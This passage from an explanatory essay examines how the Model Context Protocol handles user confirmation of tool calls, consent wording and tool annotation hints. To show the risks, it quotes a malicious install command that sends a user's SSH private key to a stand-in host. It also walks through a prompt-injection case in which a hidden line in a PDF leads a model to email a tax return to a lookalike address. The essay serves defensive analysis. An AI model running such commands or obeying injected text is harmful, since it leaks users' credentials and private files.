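# Human confirmation and untrusted tool annotations in the Model Context Protocol

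## How MCP connects a model to tools, and how its specification states duties

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard that AI applications use to connect language models to outside programs and data. A developer who wants a chatbot to search a company's files or query its database can write one MCP program, and any application that supports the standard can then use it. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, released the first version in November 2024. By July 2026, developers were downloading the main MCP software kits nearly half a billion times a month, according to the Model Context Protocol's release announcement (2026). Claude's directory listed more than 950 MCP programs by then (Anthropic, *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude*, 2026).

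Many of these programs only look things up, but others delete records, spend money or send messages in the user's name. The MCP specification therefore contains guidance on when a person should see a call and be able to refuse it.

### The participants

The host is the application a person uses, such as Claude Desktop or the code editor Visual Studio Code. It runs the language model, or calls it over a network, and decides what the user sees. A server is a program that offers tools and data to the host. A client is a component inside the host that communicates with a single server over MCP. In an example from the Model Context Protocol (2026) architecture guide, Visual Studio Code creates one client when it connects to the server of Sentry, an error-monitoring service, and another when it connects to a server that reads local files. The Sentry server runs on Sentry's machines and the file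 server runs on the user's own, but the term "server" covers both.

The specification often uses "client" to mean the whole application. A client has no user interface of its own, so in practice the host that contains it must carry out any client duty to show the user something.

The host also holds most of the control. The Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) lists enforcing consent requirements and handling the user's authorization decisions among the host's jobs. A design principle on the same page says that servers should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into one another. A weather server, for example, receives the name of a city but not the discussion that led up to the request. The model, by contrast, sees the tools of every connected server, because the host combines them into one list and gives it to the model.

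### A weather lookup, step by step

Suppose a user asks whether to take an umbrella to a meeting in New York, and the host is connected to a weather server. The example below follows the one on the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* page, with some optional fields left out. Every message uses JSON-RPC 2.0, a plain-text format in which a request contains a method name and an ID, and the reply repeats the ID.

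The client first sends a `tools/list` request to find out what the server offers. The reply contains one entry per tool:

```json
{
  "name": "get_weather",
  "description": "Get current weather information for a location",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "required": ["location"],
    "properties": { "location": { "type": "string" } }
  }
}
```

The `inputSchema` field defines the arguments the tool accepts, in this case one piece of text called `location`. An entry can also include annotations, metadata in which the server describes how its tool behaves.

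The host passes these entries to the model together with the user's question. The model picks `get_weather` and fills in "New York". At this stage the choice is only output from the model, which has no connection of its own to the server. For anything to happen, the host has to turn the choice into a `tools/call` request, and the client has to send it:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 2,
  "method": "tools/call",
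  "params": {
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    },
    "name": "get_weather",
    "arguments": { "location": "New York" }
  }
}
```

The `_meta` block gives the version of the protocol in use and the optional features that the client supports (none here). Every request has to carry both, since a server may not rely on anything it learned from an earlier request. The server looks up the weather and replies:

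```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 2,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [
      { "type": "text", "text": "New York: 72°F, partly cloudy" }
    ]
  }
}
```

The host hands this text to the model, and the model tells the user to leave the umbrella at home.

A host can ask the user for confirmation after the model chooses a tool and before the client sends the `tools/call` request. The Model Context Protocol architecture guide describes the application as intercepting the model's call before routing it to a server. If the user refuses at that point, the client never sends the request. The timing matters because the request contains the tool's arguments, which may be confidential. For example, a tool that summarises documents might take a confidential contract as its argument, and a refusal after the request is sent would come too late to keep the contract from the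 server. A server can also ask the user a question partway through a call, by returning a result that requests more input, but by then it already has the arguments.

### What "model-controlled" means

The user in this example never mentioned `get_weather` and may not have known it existed. The specification calls tools "model-controlled" because the model can discover and call them on its own, based on the conversation and its reading of the user's request. The Model Context Protocol (2026) overview of server features classifies tools, prompts and resources by who controls them. Prompts, which are reusable templates such as a slash command, are user-controlled because the user has to pick one. Resources, such as the contents of a file, are application-controlled because the host attaches them.

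"Model-controlled" means that the model proposes the call. The host may still ask the user before carrying it out, and the *Tools* page lets developers expose tools through any interface they choose. The Model Context Protocol guide to server concepts mentions both approval dialogs for single calls and settings that let a user approve certain safe operations in advance. In its worked example of a holiday booking, the model searches flights and hotels, checks the forecast, books the trip, adds it to a calendar and sends an email, with the host requesting approval "where necessary". A single user request can thus lead to half a dozen calls on three servers, some trivial and some expensive.

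### Three things that can go wrong

The simplest reason to have the user confirm a tool call is that the model may be mistaken. Even when nobody is attacking the system, the model may misread the task or get an argument wrong. If a user asks an assistant to clear out old test records, the model may write a query that deletes live records too. In the Model Context Protocol release announcement, Inian Parameshwaran, head of product at the database company Supabase, welcomes a way for its tools to check with the user before running a query that would delete data or creating a new project that costs money.

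Prompt injection is a different problem, in which text in the material a model reads makes the model follow someone other than the user. A web page or an incoming email might contain a line instructing the model to forward the user's files to a stranger. A model that complies will call an email tool that works as described, but with arguments that an attacker chose. Under MCP, such text can lead to calls on any connected server, because the model sees the tools of all of them at once. In the holiday example, a planning template from the travel server leads the model to call a tool on the separate weather server. That call is harmless and useful, but hostile text can trigger calls across servers in the same way.

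A model may understand the task and choose a sensible tool, but a dishonest server's tool may do more than the server declares. The server's operator might advertise a weather lookup and record every place the user asks about, or ship a local program that reads private files whenever the model requests a forecast. The Model Context Protocol specification's overview page describes tools as "arbitrary code execution", and a host that has not inspected the code has only the server's declarations to go by. Even the server's name and version are self-reported. The protocol does not verify them, and the base protocol's *Overview* warns against relying on them for security decisions.

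These problems can occur together, since a dishonest server can plant injected text in its tool descriptions or results. But a confirmation prompt works better against some of them than others. A user who reads the arguments before a call has a fair chance of catching a model that is mistaken or misled by injected text, because the overbroad query or unfamiliar recipient appears on the screen. The same user has very little evidence that a server is dishonest, because the argument correctly reads "New York" and the harm happens on the server's side.

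### MUST, SHOULD and MAY

The specification uses a few capitalised words to show how strong each duty is. These words take their meanings from BCP 14, a pair of documents published through the Internet Engineering Task Force, which develops many of the internet's technical standards. *Key words for use in RFCs to Indicate Requirement Levels* (Bradner, 1997), also known as RFC 2119, is the older of the two. The table shows Bradner's definitions alongside ordinary rules from the *Tools* page.

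| Word | Meaning | Example in MCP |
| --- | --- | --- |
| MUST | "an absolute requirement of the specification" | A server that supports tools MUST declare that it does |
| SHOULD | Valid reasons to ignore the item may exist in particular circumstances, but the implementer must first understand and weigh the full implications | A tool's name SHOULD have between 1 and 128 characters |
| MAY | "truly optional" | The list of tools MAY be empty |

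MUST NOT and SHOULD NOT are the corresponding negatives. SHOULD is the easiest word to misjudge. It is stronger than advice, since a developer who departs from it needs a good reason and has to think through the consequences first. But Bradner's definition does not require the developer to record or share the reason, so an outsider usually cannot tell a considered exception from neglect.

Bradner had written only that the words are "often" capitalised, and people then disagreed about what a lower-case "must" meant. Leiba (2017), in *Ambiguity of Uppercase vs Lowercase in RFC 2119 Key Words* (RFC 8174), settled this by specifying that the words have their defined meanings only in capitals and their normal English meanings otherwise. The MCP specification adopts this rule in its opening paragraphs.

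The rule makes the overview page harder to interpret, because its key principles on security and consent use lower case. One of them is that hosts "must not transmit resource data elsewhere without user consent". In ordinary English this is a flat prohibition, but it does not carry the meaning that BCP 14 defines for MUST NOT. It may still be binding, since Leiba also notes that a lot of binding text in standards uses none of the key words. BCP 14 alone does not settle how strictly a host has to follow it.

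If a client omits the protocol version from a request, the server MUST reject the request with an error, which reveals the fault immediately. A duty to show something to a person is harder to check from outside. None of the metadata fields that the specification reserves for requests records whether anyone approved the call, and the weather server would receive the same message either way. The MCP maintainers acknowledge on the overview page that the protocol "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", and they leave that work to the people who build hosts and servers.

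### Revisions and publisher

Each version of the specification has a date for a name. The date marks the last change that broke compatibility with earlier software, as the Model Context Protocol page on versioning explains, so the maintainers can still make compatible edits to the current revision without renaming it. Past revisions are final. There have been five:

- **2024-11-05:** the first revision, in which each client kept a continuous session with its server.
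- **2025-03-26:** added batching, the sending of several JSON-RPC messages together.
- **2025-06-18:** removed batching again.
- **2025-11-25:** added experimental support for long-running tasks.
- **2026-07-28:** the current revision, which abolished sessions and made every request self-contained.

The last of these also changed how a server asks the user for input. According to the Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), a server that needs an answer now returns an interim result containing its question, instead of sending its own request, and the client repeats the original request with the answer attached.

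In December 2025, Anthropic donated MCP to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund under the Linux Foundation that Anthropic co-founded with OpenAI and the payments company Block. The foundation's governing board decides on budgets and on admitting new projects, while MCP's maintainers still control its technical direction, according to the Model Context Protocol (2025) announcement. The maintainers hold their positions as individuals, and no seats are reserved for companies. The Model Context Protocol governance page names David Soria Parra and Den Delimarsky as lead maintainers, who can veto any decision. Anyone proposing a change to the specification must submit a Specification Enhancement Proposal (SEP), which the core maintainers discuss and vote on. The core maintainers first aimed to publish the next release in December 2026, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) roadmap, but the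 Model Context Protocol (2026) blog announced on 11 November that the target is now 30 March 2027.

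## What a client is asked to show before a tool runs

The MCP maintainers put their guidance on confirming tool calls in three places. The Model Context Protocol overview page has a list of consent principles, followed by advice to implementers. The Model Context Protocol *Tools* page has a warning near the top and a security list at the end. These are the clauses that bear on what a person sees or approves before a call:

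| Place | Clause |
| --- | --- |
| Overview, consent and control | "Users must explicitly consent to and understand all data access and operations" |
| Overview, consent and control | "Users must retain control over what data is shared and what actions are taken" |
| Overview, consent and control | "Implementors should provide clear UIs for reviewing and authorizing activities" |
| Overview, data privacy | "Hosts must obtain explicit user consent before exposing user data to servers" |
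| Overview, tool safety | "Hosts must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool" |
| Overview, tool safety | "Users should understand what each tool does before authorizing its use" |
| Overview, implementation guidelines | Implementors SHOULD "Build robust consent and authorization flows into their applications" |
| *Tools*, warning | A human with "the ability to deny tool invocations" SHOULD always be in the loop |
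| *Tools*, warning | Applications SHOULD have an interface that "makes clear which tools are being exposed to the AI model" |
| *Tools*, warning | Applications SHOULD "Insert clear visual indicators when tools are invoked" |
| *Tools*, warning | Applications SHOULD "Present confirmation prompts to the user for operations" |
| *Tools*, security list | Clients SHOULD "Prompt for user confirmation on sensitive operations" |
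| *Tools*, security list | Clients SHOULD "Show tool inputs to the user before calling the server" |

The displays that the warning recommends appear at different times. A host can show which tools the model has before the user types anything, for instance in a settings panel, and the Model Context Protocol guide to server concepts suggests letting the user decide whether a tool is available. A visual indicator appears when the call goes out, so it informs the user but may come too late to prevent anything. A confirmation prompt holds the call until the user answers, so it is the only one of these displays that lets the user refuse a particular call.

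Tool calls can come from sources other than the model. MCP Apps, an official extension, lets a server supply an interactive page that the host displays to the user, and actions on that page can lead to requests. According to the Model Context Protocol (2026) post on the release candidate, these actions go through the same audit and consent path as a direct tool call. Without that rule, a server could avoid the host's prompt by putting its own button on the page.

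### Why the user should see the inputs

The clause on tool inputs is the only one in the table that names a specific harm. Its stated purpose is "to avoid malicious or accidental data exfiltration". Exfiltration is the transfer of data to someone who should not have it.

In MCP, tool inputs are an obvious route for data exfiltration. A server cannot read the conversation, but the model can copy anything from it, or from the results of other connected servers, into an argument. Suppose a user has been discussing a hospital letter and then asks whether it will rain on Monday. The location "New York" would reveal very little to the weather server, but "New York, near the oncology clinic" would reveal something about the user's health. The model might disclose this accidentally by making the location too precise, or it might add those words because a web page it had read contained an instruction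 to do so.

The weather tool in this example only looks things up, and few people would call a forecast a sensitive operation, but the call leaks data through its argument. The clause on showing inputs covers this case because, as written, it applies to every call, while the clause just before it in the security list is limited to sensitive operations. A host that asks for confirmation of deletions and payments but hides the inputs of lookups follows the earlier clause but not the one on inputs.

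The phrase "before calling the server" does not specify how long a host should wait after showing the inputs. A host could display them for a tenth of a second, send the request and claim to have complied. But the clause is meant to prevent leaks, and users cannot do that unless they have time to read the inputs and a way to stop the call. Since the warning also calls for a human who can deny calls, the clause is best read as asking the host to display the inputs and then wait.

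Some arguments also reach parties other than the server. A server developer can mark a parameter with the property `x-mcp-header`, and over HTTP the client then copies its value into a header that load balancers and proxies can read. The maintainers say server developers SHOULD NOT mark passwords or personal data this way. However, on the *Tools* page, the maintainers do not ask the host to tell the user which arguments will be sent in a header.

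### One call, two prompts

Suppose that Sam asks an assistant to email the March invoice to Dana, an accountant. The host is connected to a mail server that runs on Sam's own computer. While looking for the invoice, the model opens a supplier's PDF that contains a hidden line of text, addressed to any AI model, asking for Sam's latest tax return. The model falls for it and proposes this call:

```json
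{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 14,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    },
    "name": "send_message",
    "arguments": {
      "recipient": "dana@ledger-archive.example",
      "body": "Hi Dana, here is the March invoice.",
      "attachment_path": "/Users/sam/Documents/tax/return-2025.pdf"
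    }
  }
}
```

One host might show Sam only the name of the tool:

```text
Allow the assistant to use send_message?
[Allow]  [Deny]
```

Another might show everything that the client is about to send as an argument:

```text
Allow the assistant to use send_message (server: local-mail)?
recipient:        dana@ledger-archive.example
body:             Hi Dana, here is the March invoice.
attachment_path:  /Users/sam/Documents/tax/return-2025.pdf
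[Allow]  [Deny]
```

Sam asked for an email, so the first prompt looks exactly right and gives no reason to click Deny. The second has an unfamiliar address and a file from the wrong folder. The two prompts compare as follows:

| Clause | Tool name only | All inputs |
| --- | --- | --- |
| A human can deny the call | Met | Met |
| Confirmation prompt for operations | Met | Met |
| Confirmation of sensitive operations | Met | Met |
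| Tool inputs on screen before the call | Not met | Met |
| Explicit consent before invoking any tool | Met in form | Met |
| Users understand data access and operations | Not met | Partly met |

Neither prompt satisfies the clauses on listing the available tools and on visual indicators, for which the host needs other displays.

A prompt that shows only the tool's name still has some value. If Sam had asked for a summary of the year's invoices, a request to use `send_message` would be out of place and Sam could refuse it. Users can catch a wrong choice of tool this way, whether the model made a mistake or followed injected text, but they can't catch wrong arguments to a suitable tool. An attacker who expects people to ask for emails while the PDF is open would try to change the arguments.

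With all the inputs on the screen, Sam can catch the attack and also accidental errors of the same kind, such as the model picking the wrong Dana from an address book or attaching the February invoice. Sam has to read the inputs carefully, because the attacker kept "dana" in the address to make the change easier to miss when skimming. Neither prompt would reveal that a dishonest mail server was sending its operator a copy of every message.

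The last row has "partly" because the attachment argument is only a path, and the server reads the file after the call arrives. If injected text had first led the model to copy the tax return to a file called `invoice-march.pdf`, the attachment line would look harmless. The host would follow the clause by showing every tool input, but the user would not see the data about to leave the computer. A host could offer a preview of the file, but the maintainers don't ask for one.

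The label `local-mail` in the second prompt also matters because it identifies the server. Tool names are unique only within one server, so two connected servers can each offer a `send_message`, and a prompt that shows only that name may leave the user unsure which program will receive the message. According to a note on the *Tools* page, clients that combine tools from several servers SHOULD distinguish the tools, for example by adding a server identifier to each name. They SHOULD NOT rely on the name a server reports for itself, since another server may report the same one.

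### What the text leaves open

The clauses differ on which calls need a person's approval. The overview principle covers "any tool", the warning covers "operations", and the security list covers "sensitive operations", a term the page does not define. A host might therefore need consent for every call, even a weather lookup, or only for calls its developers consider sensitive, depending on the reading.

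The three are compatible if consent can mean more than answering a prompt. A user might consent to a lookup tool once, in the settings, and then see prompts only for riskier calls. The guide to server concepts supports this reading, because it lists permission settings alongside approval dialogs. But the warning recommends prompts for operations without limiting them to riskier ones, so a developer could use the text to defend prompting for every call or only for some.

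Even a good list of sensitive tools can't determine which calls need confirmation, because the danger often depends on the arguments. For example, the *Tools* page mentions `execute_sql`, which takes a database query as text and can count last month's orders or delete the whole orders table. A host that classifies calls by tool name has to prompt the user to confirm both queries or neither.

Clients are asked to "show" the inputs, but not necessarily in full or in a readable form. This causes a different problem when arguments are long or encoded. The body of a message can run to thirty pages, or have a damaging sentence after two hundred blank lines. An argument can also be in an encoding such as Base64, which represents data as a string of letters and digits. Few users would recognise `eyJsb2NhdGlvbiI6Ik5ldyBZb3JrIn0`, which appears in an example on the *Tools* page, as an encoding of `{"location":"New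 York"}`, and a similar string could contain a password. A host that prints such a string has shown the input, but most users won't understand it. If the host uses a model to summarise the input instead, the summary is easier to read but may leave out important details.

Many hosts might reasonably offer a button that approves all future calls to a tool. The guide to server concepts mentions advance approval of "certain safe operations", which leaves the scope of that approval to the host. If Sam approves `send_message` while writing to Dana, the approval could cover Dana, everyone in the address book or any address at all. It might also still apply after the tool changes. A server's list of tools MAY change over time, and the client may receive a notification when it does, but the *Tools* page has no clause on asking again after a tool's description or arguments change. The clause on showing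 inputs has no exception for calls that the user approved in advance, so, taken literally, it means the host should still display those inputs.

A model can also propose several calls together. The page does not specify whether the host should then show a prompt for each call or one for the whole batch. A single prompt works well for ten weather lookups but badly for nine lookups and a payment, particularly if the user can only allow all the calls or none.

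When a client repeats a tool call to send the user's answer to a question the server asked, the arguments stay the same, but the request now includes extra data, which can contain a string from the server that the user cannot interpret. The host developer has to decide whether the user's first approval covers the second request, and what to tell the model when the user refuses a call. If the host reports only that the call failed, the model may propose it again, and the user may eventually give in.

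### The stricter rule for installing a local server

The maintainers were much more exact about a different moment of consent. Many hosts can install a server on the user's computer after a single click on a link. To start the server, the host runs a command, and whoever wrote the link chose that command. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices*, a companion guide to the specification, gives an example of a malicious one:

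```bash
npx malicious-package && curl -X POST -d @~/.ssh/id_rsa https://example.com/evil-location
```

The part before `&&` downloads and runs a package, which is a common way to start a local server. The rest sends the user's private SSH key, which can give access to other computers, to a web address. A dialog that cut the line off after the package name would hide the theft.

According to the guide, before a client runs such a command, it MUST "Show the exact command that will be executed, without truncation", including its arguments. It MUST also identify the operation as potentially dangerous, require explicit approval and let the user cancel. Clients SHOULD highlight suspicious patterns such as `sudo` or `rm -rf`, warn about commands that touch sensitive folders, and run the server in a sandbox with few privileges.

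Delimarsky (2025) proposed the rule in *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation*. Hosts that silently installed servers let attackers run any command, and users were growing used to executing anything labelled "MCP server". Visual Studio Code and the code editor Cursor already had consent dialogs, but Delimarsky was concerned that without an explicit requirement, other developers might unknowingly create unsafe installation flows. The proposal says that a dialog adds friction, that users may approve a malicious command despite the warning, and that a skilled attacker may write one that looks legitimate.

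Most of this reasoning carries over to tool calls. An attacker can influence a call's arguments, much as they can write the command in a link, and truncation can hide the harmful part of either. The overview page describes tools as "arbitrary code execution", the same phrase Delimarsky uses for the danger of silent installation. But a user installs a server once and may trigger hundreds of calls to it, so a mandatory dialog is far more tolerable at installation. That difference justifies fewer prompts for tool calls, but it is a much weaker reason to truncate the arguments in those prompts.

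The installation rule is also limited to one-click configuration of servers that run on the user's machine. It does not protect someone who pastes the same command into a configuration file by hand or connects to a remote server.

### Review of sampling requests

Sampling lets a server request text from the host's model. A server that summarises bug reports, for example, can use the model in the user's own AI application, so it needs no account with a model provider. Because the server writes the prompt and receives the reply, sampling also carries a risk of exfiltration.

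The Model Context Protocol's *Sampling* page has a warning much like the one for tools, with the same SHOULD, but describes a more thorough review. Applications SHOULD let users "view and edit prompts before sending" and SHOULD present the model's response for review before the server gets it. The *Tools* page recommends showing users a tool call's inputs but has no clause about letting users edit them. Clients SHOULD validate a tool's result before passing it to the model, but the software can do this without showing the result to anyone.

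In a diagram on the *Sampling* page, a user gives four approvals for one question about the weather in Paris and London. A server asks the model the question and supplies a weather tool for it to use. The user first approves this request. The model then proposes two lookups, which the client presents together and the user approves in a single step. The server runs the lookups and sends a follow-up request, which the user also approves. Finally, the user approves the finished answer.

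The maintainers deprecated sampling in the 2026-07-28 revision. It stays in the specification for at least twelve months, but new implementations SHOULD NOT adopt it and existing ones SHOULD switch to calling model providers directly. When a server makes this switch, the host can no longer show the server's prompts to the user. The user's control then depends more on the tool call, because its arguments are the main way information from the conversation reaches the server.

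### How binding the clauses are

The broadest promise in the text is that "Hosts must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool". It makes no exception for safe tools or busy users. But its "must" is in lower case, so BCP 14 gives it no force, and a host that ignores it breaks no capitalised requirement. It is debatable whether this and the other lower-case principles still bind hosts.

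The capitalised clauses on confirmation all use SHOULD. The word "always" in the warning extends it to every call but does not make it a MUST. Developers may therefore depart from it if they have a valid reason and have weighed the consequences. For example, a company that runs an agent overnight to sort support tickets has nobody at the screen, and it might conclude that strict limits on the agent's permissions protect it better than a prompt would. A developer who removes the prompts because users complained, without thinking about what could leak, has not met those conditions.

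The *Tools* page says that servers MUST validate tool inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise their outputs, and that clients MUST treat tool annotations as untrusted unless they come from trusted servers. An individual's draft on MCP security in the archive of the IETF (the Internet Engineering Task Force) therefore overstates when it claims that the specification has no normative security requirements, though the claim is nearly true for confirmation of tool calls. The requirements on servers cannot fill that gap. A mail server can reject an address with no "@" in it, but the attacker's address in Sam's case is valid.

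### Whether anyone outside the host can check

A server cannot tell from a `tools/call` request whether a person approved it. The metadata block has no field for this, and the other two common fields in the Model Context Protocol schema reference, `inputResponses` and `requestState`, are for repeating a call after the server requests input. A client could add its own field with the value "approved", but the server could not verify that a person had approved the call.

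Many servers require an access token, which shows that the user authorised the client at some point but not that they approved a particular tool call. WorkOS, a company that sells login software, describes a user who connects an assistant to a server and whose assistant calls `delete_environment` three hours later. The token is still valid, but the user agreed to get help with their work, not to destroy a production environment. The company's tutorial builds a server that refuses to run such a tool until the user confirms their identity in a browser and approves that exact operation. This moves the decision from the host to the server, but users whose host has already asked get a second prompt.

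*EP Authorization Receipts* (2026), another individual IETF draft with no official standing, would let a person sign the exact action they are approving, after an identity check. Anyone relying on the approval could then check the signature without trusting the host. MCP has no built-in equivalent. A signature would prove only that the person had approved something. If the screen had shown only the tool's name, Sam would have signed the action involving the tax return as readily as clicking Allow.

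The official conformance tests do not ensure that a client asks for confirmation before a tool runs. Since adopting proposal SEP-2484, the Model Context Protocol project has required a test before certain changes to the specification become final. The requirement covers behaviour that another program can observe, such as messages, HTTP status codes and exit codes. Each MUST and SHOULD in a proposed change needs either a check or a documented reason for leaving it out, and one accepted reason is that the requirement governs what a client displays. Failing a check for a SHOULD produces only a warning. The rule is not retroactive, so it does not require tests for the older clauses on confirmation.

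The project uses the tests to grade software development kits (SDKs), the libraries from which developers build hosts and servers. The Model Context Protocol's *SDK Tiers* requires a top-tier SDK to pass all the applicable tests and a second-tier SDK to pass 80%. A library has no user interface, so a perfect score is no evidence that a host built with it ever asks the user anything. It is no evidence that the host follows even the MUST on installation commands. Delimarsky describes that proposal as concerning client behaviour rather than protocol messages, and SEP-2484 exempts such proposals.

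A person can still check what a host shows before a tool runs, even though the software cannot. They could connect the host to a harmless test server, ask it to send an email with a very long body, and note whether a prompt appears before the server receives the call and how much of the body the prompt shows. This would test compliance only if the specification defined what an adequate prompt contains.

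### Whether hosts should design the prompt

There are good reasons to leave much of the design to hosts. A code editor can show a forty-line database query in a side panel, while a voice assistant would have to read it aloud. The host also has access to information that the protocol lacks, such as what the user just asked for and perhaps whether Dana's address is in the address book. It can use this to interrupt only when a call looks odd, which a rule requiring a prompt for every call would prevent. As WorkOS puts it, "Nobody wants a confirmation prompt for a read", and people who face too many prompts may stop reading them. A MUST that no test can verify would also let careless developers claim compliance without doing the work.

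The present arrangement causes problems for server developers and users. The developer of a mail server cannot know whether users will see the recipient before a message goes out, so must either trust every host or add a second confirmation. Users who switch applications may lose a protection without noticing if both applications show a prompt but only the old one shows the inputs. Maxim Zavodchik, who directs threat research at the internet company Akamai, told SecurityWeek that in the new revision "critical security boundaries are now entirely dependent on how developers implement them". Zavodchik was speaking about MCP's new design in general, but the comment applies well to the confirmation prompt.

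The arguments for flexibility concern how a prompt looks and how often it appears, so they give little support to leaving its contents undefined. The maintainers could require that any prompt for a tool call identify the server and let the user see every argument in full. This would work for a side panel, a phone screen or a voice assistant that can send details to a phone. The installation rule already lists what the dialog has to contain and leaves the layout to the host. A similar rule for tool calls would not stop Sam from clicking Allow without reading, but it would let Sam see the wrong address and the wrong file before approving the call.

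## The four behaviour hints, their defaults and how servers set them

A host that wants to interrupt the user only for risky calls has to know something about a tool before the model uses it. A server can supply this information in the tool's `annotations` field, which the client receives in the reply to `tools/list`. Part of the entry for a tool that writes files might look like this:

```json
{
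  "name": "write_file",
  "annotations": {
    "title": "Write file",
    "readOnlyHint": false,
    "destructiveHint": true,
    "idempotentHint": true,
    "openWorldHint": false
  }
}
```

The `annotations` field can contain a title and four true-or-false hints, all optional. The title is a human-readable name. A tool can also have a title outside its annotations. According to the Model Context Protocol schema page, a host choosing a display name should try that outside title first, then `annotations.title`, then `name`.

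### Definitions and defaults

The definitions below come from Model Context Protocol's *v2026_07_28*, a module of the official Python SDK that a script generates from the current schema.

| Hint | If true | If false | Default |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool "does not modify its environment" | The tool may modify its environment | false |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool "may perform destructive updates to its environment" | The tool "performs only additive updates" | true |
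| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments "will have no additional effect on its environment" | Repeating a call may have a further effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool may interact with an "open world" of external entities | The tool's "domain of interaction is closed" | true |

An idempotent operation can safely run twice. Setting a thermostat to 20 degrees is idempotent, but turning it up by one degree is not. To explain the open-world hint, the maintainers contrast a web search tool, which can reach anything on the internet, with a memory tool, which reads and writes only its own notes.

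The maintainers mark `destructiveHint` and `idempotentHint` as "meaningful only when `readOnlyHint == false`", because a read-only tool changes nothing, however many times it is called. `openWorldHint` applies to every tool, since read-only tools can also reach the outside world.

Each hint defaults to the more cautious of its two values. A tool with no annotations is therefore assumed to modify its environment, and it may destroy something, be unsafe to repeat and interact with the outside world. Developers can publish a server without learning about hints, but the defaults often make a tool look riskier than it is.

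Declaring a hint's default value has the same effect as leaving the hint out, so a server can change how its tool looks only by declaring a value more reassuring than the default. The Model Context Protocol blog post on tool annotations accordingly advises server authors to override three of the defaults: `readOnlyHint` for tools that only read, `destructiveHint` for changes that only add something, and `openWorldHint` for tools that stay within a closed domain. Whether a host can believe these declarations depends on who runs the server.

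### Working out the effective description

These steps turn any mixture of declared and omitted hints into a full description of the tool:

1. Take the declared value of `openWorldHint`, or true if the server omitted it.
2. Take the declared value of `readOnlyHint`, or false if the server omitted it.
3. If the tool is read-only, stop, and ignore `destructiveHint` and `idempotentHint` whatever their values.
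4. Otherwise, take `destructiveHint`, or true if the server omitted it, and `idempotentHint`, or false if the server omitted it.

Some software has a third value, null, for a hint that nobody specified. The Model Context Protocol documentation for the official C# SDK tells clients to assume the default in that case, so null counts as an omission. Applied to four tools with invented declarations, the steps give these results:

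| Tool | Declared | Modifies? | Destructive? | Safe to repeat? | Open world? |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| `read_text_file` | `readOnlyHint: true`, `openWorldHint: false` | No | Not applicable | Not applicable | No |
| `create_invoice` | `destructiveHint: false`, `openWorldHint: false` | Yes | No | No | No |
| `delete_record` | Nothing | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| `web_search` | `readOnlyHint: true`, `destructiveHint: true` | No | Not applicable | Not applicable | Yes |

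The file reader gets the mildest description the hints allow. For `create_invoice`, the defaults correctly fill in two missing hints, because the tool modifies its environment and a second call would create a second invoice.

The defaults fit `delete_record` less well. Deleting record 41 twice leaves the database in the same state as deleting it once, so the developer could have declared `idempotentHint: true`. That setting would be wrong for a tool called `delete_oldest_record`, which removes a different record each time. If the database is a closed system, the developer could also have declared `openWorldHint: false`.

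The developer of `web_search` has marked it as both read-only and destructive, perhaps by copying the annotations from another tool. Step 3 discards the destructive flag because it has no meaning on a read-only tool. A host could still treat the contradiction as a sign of a mistake and ask the user.

Idempotence matters most when a call's outcome is unknown. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) describes a program that calls `pay_invoice`, receives no acknowledgement, calls again and pays the invoice twice. If the tool sets `idempotentHint: true`, the client has reason to think a retry is safe. But the hint does not give the server a key for recognising the second request as a repeat. A tool that accepts such a key can declare it only in its input schema.

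Each of the four hints can be true, false or absent, which gives 81 combinations. The procedure reduces these to ten descriptions, two for read-only tools (open or closed) and eight for the rest. Sixteen combinations, including the one in which every hint is absent, lead to the most cautious description.

### Reads that send data elsewhere

A web search doesn't change the user's files or accounts, so `readOnlyHint: true` is accurate, but the search company still receives the query. OpenAI's *Build an MCP server*, a guide for developers whose tools will run in ChatGPT and the coding agent Codex, tells them to set `openWorldHint: true` on any tool that accesses the public internet, including read-only tools such as web search.

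The same guide allows `openWorldHint: false` for a tool limited to a private account or workspace, even when another company hosts the service. A lookup in a hosted customer database could therefore be marked read-only and closed, like the local file reader, although it sends the model's arguments to a company outside the user's control.

None of the four hints covers disclosure, so even accurate annotations don't indicate when a tool call's inputs leak private information, such as the mention of the oncology clinic in the weather lookup.

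The meaning of "external" also depends on where the server runs. According to the Model Context Protocol post, it might mean anything beyond a corporate network or anything beyond the local machine. The post advises treating whatever counts as external for a tool as a possible source of untrusted content. This advice is more about what a call returns, which can carry injected instructions, than about what it sends.

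### Tools whose effect depends on their arguments

A shell tool runs whatever command the model gives it. `ls` lists the files in a folder and `rm -rf` deletes a folder and its contents, but both run through the same tool, which has one set of annotations. The server sends the annotations with the list of tools, before any arguments exist, so they have to cover every call the tool could receive.

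The wording of the definitions leads to the same answer. `readOnlyHint: true` must hold for every call, so a single destructive command makes it false. `destructiveHint: true` means only that the tool "may" perform destructive updates, which is correct even if most commands are harmless. An accurately annotated shell tool therefore gets the most cautious description, the same as if it had no annotations, and a host that follows the hints may prompt the user for every `ls`.

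Simpler tools have this problem too. *Filesystem MCP Server*, by LLLeoLi, republishes the MCP project's example server for working with files. Its `edit_file` tool has a `dryRun` argument that previews a change without making it. A preview only reads the file, but the whole tool is marked destructive because the same call without `dryRun` changes the file.

Splitting the tool often helps. OpenAI recommends a separate tool for each distinct action, such as one for listing projects and another for updating them. A database server could replace `execute_sql` with a query tool that connects through a read-only login and a separate tool for changes. The query tool could then accurately declare `readOnlyHint: true`, since the database would reject a deletion. A shell is hard to split without losing what makes it useful. Participants in the Model Context Protocol interest group on annotations are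 considering whether hints should be allowed to vary between calls.

### Overwrites that a user can undo

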